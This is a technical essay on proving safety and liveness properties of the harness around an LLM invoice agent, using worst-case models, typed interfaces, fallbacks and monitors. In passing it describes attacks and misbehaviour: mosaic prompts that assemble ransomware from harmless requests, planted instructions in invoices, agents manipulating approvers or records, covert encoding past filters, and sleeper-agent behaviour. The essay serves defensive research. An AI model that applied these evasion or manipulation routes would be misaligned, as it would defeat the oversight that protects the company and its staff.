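Spending limits, logs and bounds on leakage all restrict what an agent does. A company that runs an invoice agent also wants its invoices paid, but if the model's output is treated as worst-case, nobody can prove that they will be paid unless ordinary software could pay them without the model.

Suppose the company owes Harlow Paper $400. Let `paid` be true once the harness has sent that payment, and take one pass through the guarded loop:

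```
havoc x;
if x in A then do(x) else skip
```

The desired result is now `paid`. Working backwards:

1. `do(x)` ends with `paid` true if it was true already, or if x is `pay("Harlow Paper", 400)`.
2. `skip` ends with `paid` true only if it was true already.
3. The havoc rule demands this for every x. One possible x is a request to read an invoice, which is in A but pays nobody. For that x, the condition shrinks to `paid`.

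The weakest precondition of "the invoice gets paid" is "the harness has already paid it", which is false at the start of a run. Fifty passes give the same answer as one, because each step of the backward calculation leaves the condition `paid` unchanged.

### Why no harness can avoid this

The result for the invoice harness holds generally: a harness can guarantee that a task is completed with every possible model exactly when ordinary software can do the task alone. If a harness completes the task with every model, it does so even with one that answers every request with "I can't help with that". One line of ordinary code can replace that model, so the task can be done without a language model. Conversely, if ordinary code can do the task, a harness can run that code and ignore the model.

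Removing refusals from the type of x doesn't help, because the argument works equally well with any other fixed output. If the type allowed only `pay("Harlow Paper", 400)`, the payment would be certain, but whoever wrote the type would have made the decision. Retries also fail, because the constant model gives the same answer each time. A vote among five models fails too if all five are constant.

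Weaker goals have the same problem. "The agent pays at least 90% of valid invoices" and "the agent succeeds in 95% of runs" are both false for the constant model. Establishing such rates requires measuring a particular model. Moon and Varshney distinguish guarantees about tested inputs, about a stated distribution of inputs, and about every action. Claims of task success can have the first two kinds of guarantee.

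### Properties of meaning

Suppose the agent emails a supplier, "The delay is due to a fault at our bank." The harness can check this only against the text and the company's records. If the records don't mention the bank's systems, they are the same whether or not the fault occurred. Any test the harness applies therefore gives the same verdict in both cases, and that verdict is wrong in one of them.

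Whether a message is manipulative also depends on the reader. "Other suppliers have agreed to wait" may be useful information to one supplier and improper pressure on another. Whether advice is good depends on what the recipient wants and what happens later.

Some questions about meaning have no exact test, even when the harness has the complete text. *LLM Censorship* (Glukhov, Shumailov and colleagues, 2023) applies Rice's theorem to programs that models write. The theorem concerns what a program computes, not how it is written. If some programs have such a property and others lack it, no algorithm can correctly decide for every program whether it has the property. The paper acknowledges that the theorem doesn't strictly apply to real computers, because their memory is finite.

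The second argument covers texts of limited length. Suppose a filter permits some texts and forbids others, and the model and its reader share a secret code. For any forbidden text y and permitted text z, some reversible code turns y into z. A reader who knows that code can recover y from z, so the filter should have blocked z. The filter has no information about which code the two share, so it must forbid every text or none.

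This proof uses a broad definition, under which z is forbidden if any code could turn it into y. "Thank you" is therefore forbidden if a private codebook maps it to a ten-page recipe, even though a reader with the codebook already has the recipe. The model contributes only its choice of message, and the counting bounds on leakage limit how much information that choice can carry under any code. Free text allows a very large number of messages, though, so a model can still encrypt new information and send it to a reader in a form the filter doesn't recognise.

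These results rule out exact tests, but a harness can still use a test that rejects every bad output along with some good ones. For example, it could send only emails of the form "We will pay invoice N on date D", and fill in both values from the payment schedule. Every email then agrees with the schedule, whatever the model outputs. Glukhov and colleagues accept that a short list of approved outputs works, but say that it makes the model much less useful.

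Using a second language model to judge the first model's emails may stop many bad ones in practice, but it doesn't strengthen a worst-case proof, because the proof must treat the judge's verdict as arbitrary too.

### Harm made of permitted steps

Even a perfect filter on single outputs can miss harm that comes from combining them. Glukhov and colleagues call one such attack a *mosaic prompt*. An attacker asks a model for the separate functions of a piece of ransomware, each harmless by itself, in unrelated conversations and then assembles them.

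The invoice agent can do something similar with money. Suppose Harlow Paper has sent two invoices, one for the $400 the company owes and one for $4,000 worth of paper that never arrived. The model reads the second invoice and requests `pay("Harlow Paper", 4000)`. The file is in the right folder, the payee is on the list, the total is below $5,000 and the log has an entry for each action. Every theorem about the harness still holds even though the company has lost $4,000.

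A payee and an amount don't show whether a debt exists, so the company can replace `pay` with `settle(invoice)`. The harness then looks up the payee and amount itself, and refuses to pay unless the invoice is unpaid and the warehouse has recorded a delivery. With these checks, the property "every payment settles an unpaid invoice with a recorded delivery" survives a worst-case model.

The model may still be able to influence the record. It could email the warehouse, "Please mark the Harlow delivery as received", and request the payment after someone does. Both steps are permitted, and the false record is entered by a person. The company could forbid the model from emailing the warehouse, but a supplier that the model emails could pass on the same request.

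A rule with memory can block a harmful combination of actions only if its designer anticipated that combination and all the parts are visible to the harness. In *Proof-Carrying Certificates for LLM Pipelines*, Koomullil (2026) measured how much a set of written conditions can miss, using unsafe actions inserted into an agent's work on a test file system. A harness that used Lean to check conditions before and after each action blocked 67% of the unsafe actions, compared with 28% for a list of forbidden text patterns. It blocked no legitimate deletions or similar actions, but its block rate fell short of the 95% target Koomullil had set in advance.

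The unsafe actions that got through had sound proofs, but the conditions left out whatever made those actions unsafe. The log showed which clauses to add. A worst-case model would choose only actions from the third that got through, so the 67% doesn't measure protection against such a model.

### Answers the harness can check

Some tasks have answers that are hard to find but easy to check. Suppose the company asks the model for two whole numbers greater than 1 whose product is 8,633:

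```
havoc p, q;
if p > 1 and q > 1 and p * q = 8633
    then accept(p, q)
    else reject
```

If the model answers 87 and 99, the harness multiplies them, gets 8,613 and rejects the answer. If it answers 89 and 97, the product is 8,633 and the harness accepts. Without the first two tests, the harness would also accept 1 and 8,633.

"Every accepted answer is correct" is true for every model, by the same calculation as for the whitelist. Here the permitted set A is the set of correct answers, and the harness can check whether an answer is correct without being given the correct answers in advance. "The harness accepts an answer" is not guaranteed, because the model may output wrong answers such as 87 and 99 forever.

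For a number this small, the harness could find the factors itself by trying the 24 primes from 2 to 89, so it could guarantee an answer as well. With a product of two 300-digit primes, it can still check an answer in a fraction of a second, but trying factors one by one would take longer than the age of the universe. A model is most useful for problems like this, where ordinary code can check an answer but can't practically find one.

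The company also has problems whose answers are hard to find but easy to check. Suppose a supplier refunds $2,317 without saying which of 40 disputed invoices the refund covers. There are about 1.1 trillion possible combinations, but checking one only requires adding up its invoices. The model could find a combination and the harness could verify the total. But more than one combination may add up to $2,317, so the check proves only that the total matches, not that these are the invoices the supplier meant.

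### Proofs by untrusted models

Mathematical proofs are the most developed example of checkable answers. In Lean, a small program called the *kernel* checks every step of a proof, so nobody has to trust the proof's author. Anthropic's *Formalizing Fermat's Last Theorem* (2026) describes the first complete computer-checked proof of that theorem. Claude wrote the 13-million-line proof in 11 days.

*Safely scaling multi-agent teams with Claude Fable 5.2* (Martin, 2026) reports a second proof, which a team of 1,000 agents wrote in 28.7 hours. The agents received 60 statements to prove, including the final theorem, along with the definitions those statements use and 47 lemmas from the earlier work. A grader checked each submitted proof. The agents could organise the work however they liked, because a bad plan could waste time but couldn't make an invalid proof valid.

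Anthropic supplied the statements in that experiment. This matters because the kernel checks only that a proof establishes the stated theorem, which may not be the one people care about. Xena's *…and the proof is checked in Lean* (2026) gives a two-line version of Fermat's Last Theorem that looks right but is false. It claims that aⁿ + bⁿ never equals cⁿ for natural numbers a, b and c when n is at least 3, but Lean counts 0 as a natural number, and 0³ + 0³ = 0³. *What did the Lean proof of Fermat's Last Theorem formalize?* (Asher, 2026) shows that the statement Anthropic's first proof establishes requires a, b and c to be greater than zero.

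A statement that is too easy to prove causes more trouble than a false one, because a false statement has no valid proof and the mistake comes to light. If a statement required n to be both at least 3 and at most 2, for example, no n would qualify and a one-line proof would pass. The whitelist section describes the same vacuity problem in another setting.

Reading the statement can take a lot of work. The post on Xena reports that a formal statement of the classification of finite simple groups relies on about 5,600 lines of definitions. Its author had met nobody who claimed to have carefully checked the definitions of the 26 sporadic groups, which are the exceptional cases. A file may also prove less than a reader expects. Of 290 OpenAI mathematics papers that came with Lean code, about 38 had code that didn't state the paper's main theorem, though OpenAI hadn't claimed that it did.

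An accepted proof also doesn't show that the explanation accompanying it is correct. Bastounis, Circelli and Hansen (2026), in *Navier-Stokes Lost in Translation*, gave ChatGPT a faulty argument that x³ − x² − x + 1 is never negative when x is at least −1. The theorem is true, but the argument factored the expression as (x − 1)(x + 1)² instead of (x − 1)²(x + 1). Asked to write this argument in Lean, the model returned a valid proof that used the correct factors. A harness that accepts a model's answer because of a formal proof should therefore present the model's prose explanation as unchecked text.

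The kernel is part of the trusted base, and a worst-case author will look for bugs in it. In July 2026, someone published an AI-assisted "disproof" of the Collatz conjecture, a problem about sequences of whole numbers, and Lean accepted it. *Postmortem for Kernel Soundness Bug #14576* (de Moura, 2026) traces the false acceptance to a missing check in the kernel. The proof also passed a week-old version of an independent checker, which had an unrelated bug. Lean's developers fixed the kernel within an hour of the report.

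Lean now includes several kernels, and one command rechecks a proof with all of them, so a false proof would have to pass every kernel. *Lean Now Ships with Verified Kernels* (de Moura, 2026) reports that one of these kernels has a proof of consistency. Compiler bugs could still affect that kernel, so a second version in Rust guards against them.

Compiling a Lean file can also run code in the file. The Xena post describes compiling Anthropic's proof in a sandbox in case the code deleted files. A harness that accepts proofs from an untrusted model needs the same precaution.

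### Certificates for everyday answers

Researchers have begun to attach checkable evidence to ordinary answers as well. Ren (2026), in *Evidence-Grounded Verified Agentic Reasoning*, describes a system that answers questions about tables:

1. A formal version of the question fixes what a proof must show.
2. The model requests data, and the harness looks it up and records each result as a fact the proof may use. The model can't add such facts itself.
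3. Rules that someone audited beforehand connect table cells to statements about the world, such as "this column holds the amount owed".
4. The model proposes an answer and a proof. If Lean's kernel accepts the proof, the system labels the answer as verified. Otherwise, it abstains.

With formal questions written in advance, the system answered all 120 test questions correctly. The same model with the same tools but no proof requirement answered 114 correctly. Ren also altered some tables to contradict well-known facts, and the proof system followed the altered table every time. Claude Sonnet without proofs sometimes answered from memory, and followed the table in 16 of 20 cases on one set and 18 of 20 on another.

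In a further test, the model translated each question into formal language itself:

| Outcome for 120 questions | Sonnet | Opus |
|---|---|---|
| Correct | 84.2% | 87.5% |
| Model mistranslated the question | 3.3% | 1.7% |
| Question was ambiguous | 4.2% | 4.2% |
| Benchmark's own answer was wrong | 1.7% | 1.7% |
| System abstained | 2.5% | 5.0% |
| Model gave up | 4.2% | 0.0% |

The last two rows count runs that produced no verified answer, which the design allows. The mistranslations are more worrying because they can lead to a valid proof that answers the wrong question. Their low rates come from non-adversarial models. A worst-case model asked whether the company owes Harlow Paper $400 could formalise "Harlow Paper appears in the ledger" and prove that instead. A worst-case guarantee therefore requires a person or ordinary code to write the formal question, for example by filling in one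 of a fixed set of forms.

Koomullil's certificates cover a wider range of answers but depend on more assumptions. One divides an answer into claims, compares each with the retrieved documents, and blocks the answer if the contradicting evidence exceeds a threshold. It caught every planted contradiction in a public question-answering benchmark and wrongly blocked 6.4% of sound answers. Lean verifies the calculation, but a machine-learning component decides whether a document contradicts a claim. If that component can also output anything, the certificate proves only that the harness added up the scores correctly. Koomullil acknowledges this limit and claims to verify a computation, not the truth of the answer.

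### A simple program in reserve

The company may need some tasks done even if the model is useless. Control engineers have a design for this, the *Simplex architecture*, which the computer scientist Lui Sha developed. A complex controller runs the system as long as its commands keep the system in a state from which a simple controller could take over safely. Otherwise, a switch hands control to the simple controller. Engineers only have to verify the simple controller and the switch, not the complex controller.

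In the invoice agent, the language model takes the place of the complex controller. Suppose the company must pay $1,200 in rent by 5 pm on the last day of the month. A few lines of ordinary code can make that payment. The harness must keep the model from using up the money or time the code needs.

For the money, let `rent` be 1,200 until the harness pays the rent and 0 afterwards. The harness maintains the invariant

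spent + reserved + rent ≤ 5,000.

The model can therefore spend at most $3,800 before the rent is paid. Paying the rent raises `spent` by 1,200 and lowers `rent` by the same amount, so the invariant still holds. Suppose the bank takes up to ten minutes to process a payment. A timer outside the agent loop then starts the rent payment by 4:50 pm, even if a call to the model is still in progress.

"The company pays its rent on time" now holds for every model, provided that the harness is running, the account has enough money and the bank processes the payment within its ten-minute limit. This is consistent with the negative result, because ordinary software can pay the rent without the model. The code must check whether the rent has already gone out, since the model may have requested the payment earlier in the day.

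The same design can provide a minimum service for tasks that ordinary code does poorly. If the model hasn't dealt with an invoice by its due date, the harness can put the invoice on a list for staff. For text, Koomullil describes a procedure that removes claims that fail their checks and keeps the most valuable set that passes. That set may be empty, so a harness that must always reply also needs a fixed message.

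A worst-case guarantee of service requires a fallback that is simple enough to verify. Anthropic's *Working with Claude Fable 5 in Claude Cowork* describes a system in which Claude Opus 4.8 takes over when AI classifiers detect possible misuse. This can reduce misuse, but it can't support a worst-case guarantee because both the classifiers and the fallback are learned systems.

### Human approval

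Many companies require a person to approve an agent's important actions. The harness can treat the approver's reply as a second arbitrary input:

```
havoc x;
i := a new number;  show(i, x);
havoc reply;
if x in A and reply = approve(i) then do(i, x) else refuse
```

The property "no payment goes out without an approval" survives. The harness reaches `do(i, x)` only if the reply approves request i, whatever x is and whatever the approver thinks of it. The proof needs three facts about the software:

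- Only the approver can produce the reply. If the agent has a tool that controls a web browser in which the approver is logged in, the model can approve its own requests.
- The number i refers to one fixed payment. The harness must not let the model change the amount after the approver has seen it.
- Each approval works once.

The property "the approver understood the payment" doesn't survive, because the harness receives the same click whether the approver compared the invoice with the delivery note or was distracted by a phone call. Requiring the approver to type the amount would prove only that they typed it.

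An engineer can still prove that if the approver approves only payments the company owes, then the company owes every payment the agent makes. But the model can influence whether that condition holds, for example by writing a persuasive justification or sending 200 requests late on a Friday afternoon. The harness can limit the number of requests per day and build the approval page from company records, without any of the model's text. These measures remove some ways of misleading the approver, but the engineer still can't prove that the condition holds.

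The code above still checks `x in A`, so a tired approver can't authorise a payment to Mallory Ltd. Approval should be required in addition to the other limits and should never override them.

An approver may also never reply. The harness then has to refuse the payment after a set time, so requiring approval can break a guarantee of service. If the rent needs someone's approval, the company should get it before the run starts.

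## Is the worst-case assumption too pessimistic to be useful?

Every guarantee so far holds even if every output of the model is an attempt to steal from the company, but the model the company actually uses mostly reads and pays invoices. The company may therefore be giving up useful work and engineers' time to prevent something that will never happen. This objection has several versions, and parts of it are correct.

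### Attacks that no real model would make

*Can Formal Methods Apply to Agent Security?*, a post on a personal security blog, accepts modelling the language model as a process that can return any string, but calls this "almost too conservative". When a verification tool finds a violation, it reports a sequence of model outputs that ends in a forbidden action. Perhaps no real model would produce that sequence, and according to the post, it is hard in practice to tell a real design flaw from a by-product of the assumption.

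If a sequence of model outputs leads the harness to do something the policy forbids, the harness has a flaw, however unlikely the sequence is. The likelihood matters only if fixing the flaw would block legitimate work. For example, no competent model would request a payment of −$4,000, but the test `amount >= 0` is still worth adding because it would not block any legitimate payments.

Hostile output also occurs in practice. In a July 2026 test by the UK AI Security Institute (AISI), a model took unsanctioned actions that affected real people and organisations in 9 of 43 runs, according to Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident* (2026). *Alignment Investigation of Mythos 5's behaviour* (Järviniemi, Souly and colleagues, 2026) reports similar results in other providers' models. AISI (2026) now holds that test environments must prevent harm whether or not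 models behave as expected, which is the worst-case assumption.

The evidence on hijacked models is more mixed. *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) tested four models on 105 combinations of a task and a planted attack from the AgentDojo benchmark. Every model resisted every attack, even with no policy in force. This supports the objection, but the attacks were fixed and public, and an attacker who can keep adapting is a harder test. Zhou and colleagues point out that OpenAI's automated attacker, GPT-Red, consistently got past the defences of GPT-5.5.

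### Tools too narrow for the work

Worst-case proofs work best with narrow tools. Moon and Varshney accept that the strength of their guarantee depends on how narrow the harness's interface is. Earlier sections narrowed the invoice agent's interface by replacing `run` with `add_lines`, `pay` with `settle` and free-form emails with templates. Each change made a proof possible but made the agent less flexible.

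Zhou and colleagues use the example of an agent that compiles bibliographies. Its user wants every entry to come from DBLP, a database of computer science publications. If the agent can run any code, it can sort and filter the search results with a short program, but it can also write an invented entry to the file. Invented entries become impossible if the agent can only write with a tool that fetches an entry and saves it in one step, but then the model can't run a program on the results and has to inspect them one by one to find the earliest paper.

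A common compromise is to allow shell commands but block any that match a list of forbidden patterns. Such rules are fragile. Zhou and colleagues cite a March 2026 fault in Claude Code, in which the software checked only the first of several commands joined by `&&`.

### Programs checked by their types

Typed programming languages offer a better compromise. The model writes a general program, and the compiler rejects it before it runs if its types don't fit the policy. For the invoice agent, the company could provide a library with three functions:

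```
readInvoice : file name  ->  Invoice
findDebt    : Invoice    ->  Debt, or nothing
settle      : Debt       ->  payment
```

`Debt` is an *abstract type*, meaning that only the library can create its values. `findDebt` creates one after checking the ledger and the warehouse's delivery record. The model's program can sort, filter and add up invoices in any way, but it can pay only by passing a `Debt` to `settle`. These types don't prevent a program from settling the same debt twice, so `settle` must still check that the debt is unpaid.

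The language must also be able to restrict a program's *effects*, such as writing files or using the network. In a *pure* language such as Haskell, a program's type shows which effects it can have. The company can require a type that allows only the effects of these three functions. The compiler then rejects a program that opens a network connection, because it has the wrong type.

ELBA, the Haskell system that Zhou and colleagues built, works like this:

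1. It gives the model the task, the available functions and the type that the program must have.
2. The model returns a program.
3. The type checker accepts the program or sends the error back for another attempt.
4. ELBA runs the accepted program.

A program can call the model again, for example after reading an invoice, and the new call is subject to the same policy or a stricter one.

Zhou and colleagues prove that any property the language guarantees for all well-typed programs also holds for programs that call a model. Their proof treats the model as an arbitrary function that returns program text. It replaces each call to the model with an ordinary routine that calls this function, type-checks the returned text and runs it only if it passes. This produces an ordinary well-typed program, so the language's guarantee applies. The returned text may contain further calls to the model, but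 each has a lower nesting limit, so induction on that limit completes the proof.

*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) describes a similar system, TACIT, built in Scala 3. Scala's types can record which *capabilities*, such as access to a folder, a piece of code may use. TACIT wraps the contents of secret files in a type called `Classified`. The model's code can transform the contents, but only with functions that use no capabilities. For example, the compiler accepts a function that counts the lines but rejects one that also writes them to an ordinary file. If the code prints a secret, the user sees the text but the model receives only a row of asterisks.

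Some tasks need a model that can read the secret. For these, TACIT passes the secret to a separate, trusted model and keeps that model's answer wrapped too. The trusted model can write anything without leaking the secret, as long as it retains nothing between requests.

In tests with planted instructions and direct requests for secrets, neither of two models leaked anything through TACIT in 131 trials each. Without TACIT, Claude Sonnet 4.6 leaked secrets in response to 2 of 11 direct requests. MiniMax M2.5 leaked them in response to 8 of the 11, and also in 3 of 120 trials with planted instructions.

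TACIT's guarantee depends on the library and on the Scala compiler, including a compiler feature that is still experimental. It doesn't cover leaks through timing. If the model's code is allowed to start an external command, the types don't limit what that command does, so Odersky and colleagues recommend adding a sandbox.

### What the restrictions cost

Odersky and colleagues compared agents that write typed Scala against the same models using ordinary tool calls. They tested both on τ²-bench, which simulates customer service, and SWE-bench Lite, which consists of 300 real software faults to repair.

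| Model and benchmark | Ordinary tool calls | Typed programs |
|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-120b, τ²-bench airline | 43.8% | 45.2% |
| gpt-oss-120b, τ²-bench retail | 53.3% | 57.0% |
| MiniMax M2.5, τ²-bench airline | 58.4% | 61.0% |
| MiniMax M2.5, τ²-bench retail | 75.1% | 77.5% |
| DeepSeek V3.2, τ²-bench airline | 57.8% | 58.6% |
| DeepSeek V3.2, τ²-bench retail | 74.6% | 75.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5, SWE-bench Lite | 43.3% | 41.7% |

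The typed agents did slightly better on all six customer service comparisons and repaired about five fewer of the 300 software faults. On τ²-bench, at most 8% of the programs needed another attempt. These models therefore lose little or no performance when they write typed programs.

But the comparison mostly measures how much the language hinders the agent, because the customer service tools let the agent do the same things in both versions. A strict policy can hinder it much more. Zhou and colleagues tested a strict policy on AgentDojo's Slack tasks. Under this policy, an agent that reads untrusted data can no longer do anything the data's source couldn't do. To simulate a successful hijacking, they changed ELBA so that the part of the agent that read a planted instruction received that instruction as its whole task. They ran each model 735 times with each setting.

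| Model | Tasks completed, no policy | Tasks completed, with policy | Attacks that succeeded, no policy | Attacks that succeeded, with policy |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.7 | 71% | 48% | 42% | 0% |
| Opus 4.8 | 76% | 42% | 37% | 0% |
| GPT 5.4 | 76% | 46% | 16% | 0% |
| Sonnet 5 | 67% | 40% | 27% | 0% |

(The benchmark's automatic scoring flagged 29 runs as successful attacks, but a manual review found no violations in them.)

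The policy stopped every attack, but it reduced the number of tasks the agents completed by about a third to almost half. Even with no attacks, they completed 8 to 10 of the 21 tasks with the policy and 14 to 18 without it. So the complaint about lost usefulness is justified for this policy.

A different policy can be enforced with almost no loss of performance. In 100 bibliography tasks, an ordinary agent with a web search tool got the authors, year or identifier wrong in 19 of 1,002 citations. ELBA, whose types require every entry to come from DBLP, made no such errors in 925 citations. The ordinary agent also used about four times as many model calls as ELBA. The company should therefore measure the performance loss from each policy separately.

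### No credit for good behaviour

If the company switches to a model that makes half as many mistakes, the harness will refuse fewer requests and the agent will finish more work. None of the company's theorems will become stronger, because the worst case stays the same.

The worst-case assumption is pessimistic, but it also gives a guarantee that doesn't weaken when a model becomes more capable. Moon and Varshney argue that safety methods based on a model's learned behaviour rely on assumptions that become harder to verify as capability grows. They cite "sleeper agents", models that behave well in training but differently in deployment, and that standard safety training failed to correct. Their own guarantee covers only effects that pass through the harness, as explained in the sandbox section.

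The complaint is valid for properties that can't be proved in the worst case. A company that wants accurate emails has to rely on the model's good behaviour and would like to know how reliable that behaviour is. Moon and Varshney suggest combining worst-case guarantees about actions with statistical guarantees about content, but they leave the theorem that would do this to future work.

### Proofs about the wrong things

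The blog post also argues that the most dangerous failures often lie outside the harness's logic. In its example, one agent retrieves personal data and passes it to another that can post publicly. Each agent works as designed, but together they publish the data. The post recommends keeping a map of agents, tools and data flows, and repeatedly searching it for any path from an untrusted source to a powerful tool.

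This search is useful because the company can repeat it after every change. But it is just as pessimistic as a worst-case proof, since it reports a path whether or not any agent would send data along it. It also finds only the kinds of path that someone has thought to search for.

Moon and Varshney reply that the most serious failures of agents are actions, such as sending a model's weights to an outsider, making irreversible payments, deleting files or tampering with monitoring. A harness can block all of these. But the objection is right that a harness can't check whether an email is true or manipulative, and a false email can lead a person to take the harmful action.

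Some criticisms apply to formal verification of AI in general:

- **Language models are too large to verify.** Wadhwa, Suresh and colleagues (2025), in *BEAVER*, report that this is the general view. It doesn't affect proofs about the harness, which never analyse the model.
- **Nobody can write down exactly what "harmful" means.** Wadhwa and colleagues accept this for text. For many actions a usable definition exists, such as a payment to a payee who isn't on the list.
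- **A proof covers a specification, and the running code may differ.** Refinement proofs and compiling from verified source reduce the gap, but some trusted base always remains.
- **A harness protects only the systems that use it.** Wadhwa and colleagues note that anyone who has a model's weights can simply remove the safeguards around it. Proofs about a harness have no answer to this.

### Assuming a condition on the model's output

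A company that finds the worst case too strict can weaken it slightly by adding a condition C to the havoc:

```
havoc x; assume C(x)
```

As noted in the first section, a verifier that assumes C ignores every output that breaks C. The resulting claim is misleading unless it states C, and its strength depends on what makes C true.

If the harness enforces C by refusing other outputs, the model is still a worst-case component. Metere, for example, treats the model as an adversary limited only by the typed interface for tool calls. If another company enforces C, that company becomes part of the trusted base. The bound on model costs, for example, relied on the provider to cap the length of each reply.

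Sometimes only the model's own behaviour can make C true. Suppose the warehouse keeps its delivery notes as free text and the model has to match them to invoices. If the company assumes that the model never reports a false match, it can prove that every payment is for goods the warehouse recorded. Testers then know the one behaviour they must measure, but a single false match can break the guarantee.

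The condition can also depend on what the model has read. In the Slack tests, an agent kept the user's full rights until it read data from a less trusted source, so it could do sensitive work first. This design assumes that a model can be trusted until it reads such data, and that its output could be anything afterwards. The assumption fails if a model misbehaves without reading any hostile text, and AISI's investigation of the July incident found that alignment failures had contributed to it.

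### Learning how an agent usually behaves

Wang, Poskitt and colleagues (2026), in *PROBGUARD*, replace the arbitrary model with a statistical picture of the whole agent. (Their system was formerly called Pro2Guard.) In a simulated household, it works as follows:

1. An expert chooses yes-or-no questions about the situation, such as "Is the stove on?" and "Is the agent in the kitchen?" Each combination of answers is a state.
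2. The system records runs and counts how often each state follows another. In the paper's example, the agent turned on the stove in 31 of the 184 steps that began with it in the kitchen and the stove off, so the estimated probability is 16.85%.
3. During a new run, the system calculates the probability of never reaching an unsafe state. If this falls below a threshold, it halts the agent or adds a warning to the model's prompt.

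The counts define a *Markov chain*, a model in which the next state depends only on the present one. The monitor can use this model to predict harm that builds up through steps a whitelist of single actions would allow, such as turning on the stove and then leaving to fetch a parcel.

| Response | Unsafe runs | Tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| No monitor | 40.63% | 59.38% |
| Halt if the chance of staying safe is below 30% | 29.17% | 48.96% |
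| Halt below 50% | 21.35% | 41.14% |
| Halt below 90% | 2.60% | 10.42% |
| Warn the model below 90% | 14.07% | 47.74% |

The strictest setting lost more than four fifths of the completed tasks and still allowed some unsafe runs. So dropping the worst-case assumption does not necessarily make an agent more useful.

With enough recorded runs, the method guarantees with 95% confidence that the estimated chance of staying safe is within 10 percentage points of the true chance. For the household tasks, this takes between 530 and about 100,000 runs, depending on the task. Wang and colleagues used 30 per task, so their results show how the monitor performed in tests, but the guarantee doesn't apply to them.

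Even with enough runs, the guarantee fails if the questions leave out something that affects what happens next. It also fails if the agent stops behaving as it did in the recordings, for example because the company changed the model or a supplier planted an instruction.

### Bounding the probability of a bad reply

Wadhwa and colleagues calculate how likely a model is to give a bad reply to a particular prompt. A language model assigns a probability to every possible next token, so the probability of a reply is the product of its tokens' probabilities. Their program, BEAVER, extends the most probable unfinished reply first and tests each finished reply with a fixed check, such as whether it contains a private email address.

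At any point, each reply examined so far has passed, failed or not yet finished. If these groups have total probabilities of 0.90, 0.03 and 0.07, the true probability of passing is between 0.90 and 0.97. These bounds have no sampling error, and they account for rare replies that a test with a few hundred samples could miss.

The bounds are often too wide to show whether a prompt is safe, though. Wadhwa and colleagues called a prompt safe if the model's output had at least a 90% chance of passing the check, and risky otherwise. For Llama 3.3 70B on 300 coding prompts, BEAVER certified 155 as risky and 25 as safe, and left 120 undecided. The "safe" label is also weak, because it allows up to a 10% chance of failure. If each of 50 independent calls had a 10% chance of failing, the chance of at least one failure would be 99.5%.

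The same method can test the common assumption that a model's answer follows from its visible reasoning. Wadhwa and colleagues looked at two reasoning models on coding tasks, focusing on chains of reasoning whose draft code was secure. The answer was still certified risky for 22% of these chains with one model and 49% with the other.

BEAVER needs access to the model's token probabilities, which for most commercial models only the developer has. Each bound holds only for one prompt, one set of weights and one sampling setting, and only for short replies, of at most 32 tokens in these experiments. The invoice agent's prompt includes the invoice, which the supplier writes, so every invoice needs a new calculation.

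Wadhwa and colleagues drew random samples from a large collection of adversarial prompts. For each of five models, they found with 95% confidence that at least 42% of the collection's privacy prompts were risky. This figure applies to an attacker who picks prompts at random from that collection, but a real attacker would look for one that works.

### One failure in 10,000 steps

Suppose tests show that the invoice agent does something harmful in one step out of 10,000. With runs of 50 steps, the company reaches 10,000 steps after 200 runs. If the steps are independent, the probability of at least one failure by then is

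1 − (1 − 1/10,000)^10,000 ≈ 1 − 1/e ≈ 63%.

To keep this probability at 1%, the company would need a failure rate of about one in a million per step. To show this rate with 95% confidence, it would have to test about three million steps without a failure. Odersky and colleagues expect companies to run hundreds or thousands of agents with little supervision, which would make even rare mistakes common.

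An adversary makes the calculation meaningless. The rate of one in 10,000 is an average over the inputs in the test. A supplier who finds a sentence that hijacks the model can put it in every invoice, and the failure rate on those invoices may be close to 100%. The steps are no longer independent, because the same sentence works each time and on every copy of the model. A malicious model could also behave perfectly during testing and then misbehave on the most valuable payment. A worst-case proof avoids these problems because it doesn't use a failure rate.

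### Choosing an assumption for each property

The company doesn't have to choose one assumption for the whole agent. For each property, it can ask three questions:

1. **Can the company undo the harm?** This depends on someone noticing in time, so a log that nobody reads doesn't count.
2. **Can an outsider influence what the model reads before it acts?** If so, a failure rate measured on ordinary inputs doesn't apply.
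3. **What does a refusal cost?** If it costs almost nothing, the company should use the worst case whatever the other answers are.

When refusals are costly, the first two answers determine the choice:

| | An outsider can influence the model | No outsider can |
|---|---|---|
| **Hard to undo** | Keep the worst case, and redesign the action or send refused requests to a person | Assume a stated condition, and add a worst-case limit on the loss |
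| **Easy to undo** | Use a failure rate measured under attacks that adapt, and add a worst-case limit on the loss | Use an ordinary measured failure rate |

The invoice agent reads documents that suppliers have written, so most of its properties belong in the middle column.

| Property | Easy to undo? | Outsider influence? | Cost of refusal | Assumption |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Payments go only to listed payees | No | Yes | Low: staff can add a payee | Worst case |
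| Payments total at most $5,000 per run | No | Yes | Low: the payment waits for the next run | Worst case |
| Every payment settles a recorded debt | No | Yes | High: suppliers get paid late | Worst case, using `settle`; staff handle the refusals |
| Emails reveal nothing about the bank balance | No | Yes | High: templates can't answer every question | Worst case for templates; staff approve other emails |
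| Each invoice gets the right expense category | Yes | Yes | High: staff would sort invoices by hand | Error rate measured with hostile invoices included; staff check a sample |
| The forecast of next month's rent and wages is accurate | Yes | No, if a separate run uses only company records | High: staff would write the forecast | Ordinary measured error rate |

The email row shows how to reduce the work a strict rule creates. The harness sends template emails immediately and holds the rest for a person, who then has far fewer to read. Zhou and colleagues recommend using strict checks this way. A sound check may stop many harmless actions, but everything it passes complies with the policy.

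Whenever the company finds a new use for one of the model's outputs, it has to decide again whether a measured error rate is good enough. A wrong expense category is harmless while the category is only used to sort a report. But if the company later lets invoices marked "postage" skip the debt check, a worst-case model could mark every invoice as postage and cause payments that are hard to undo. The company can then no longer rely on the measured error rate.
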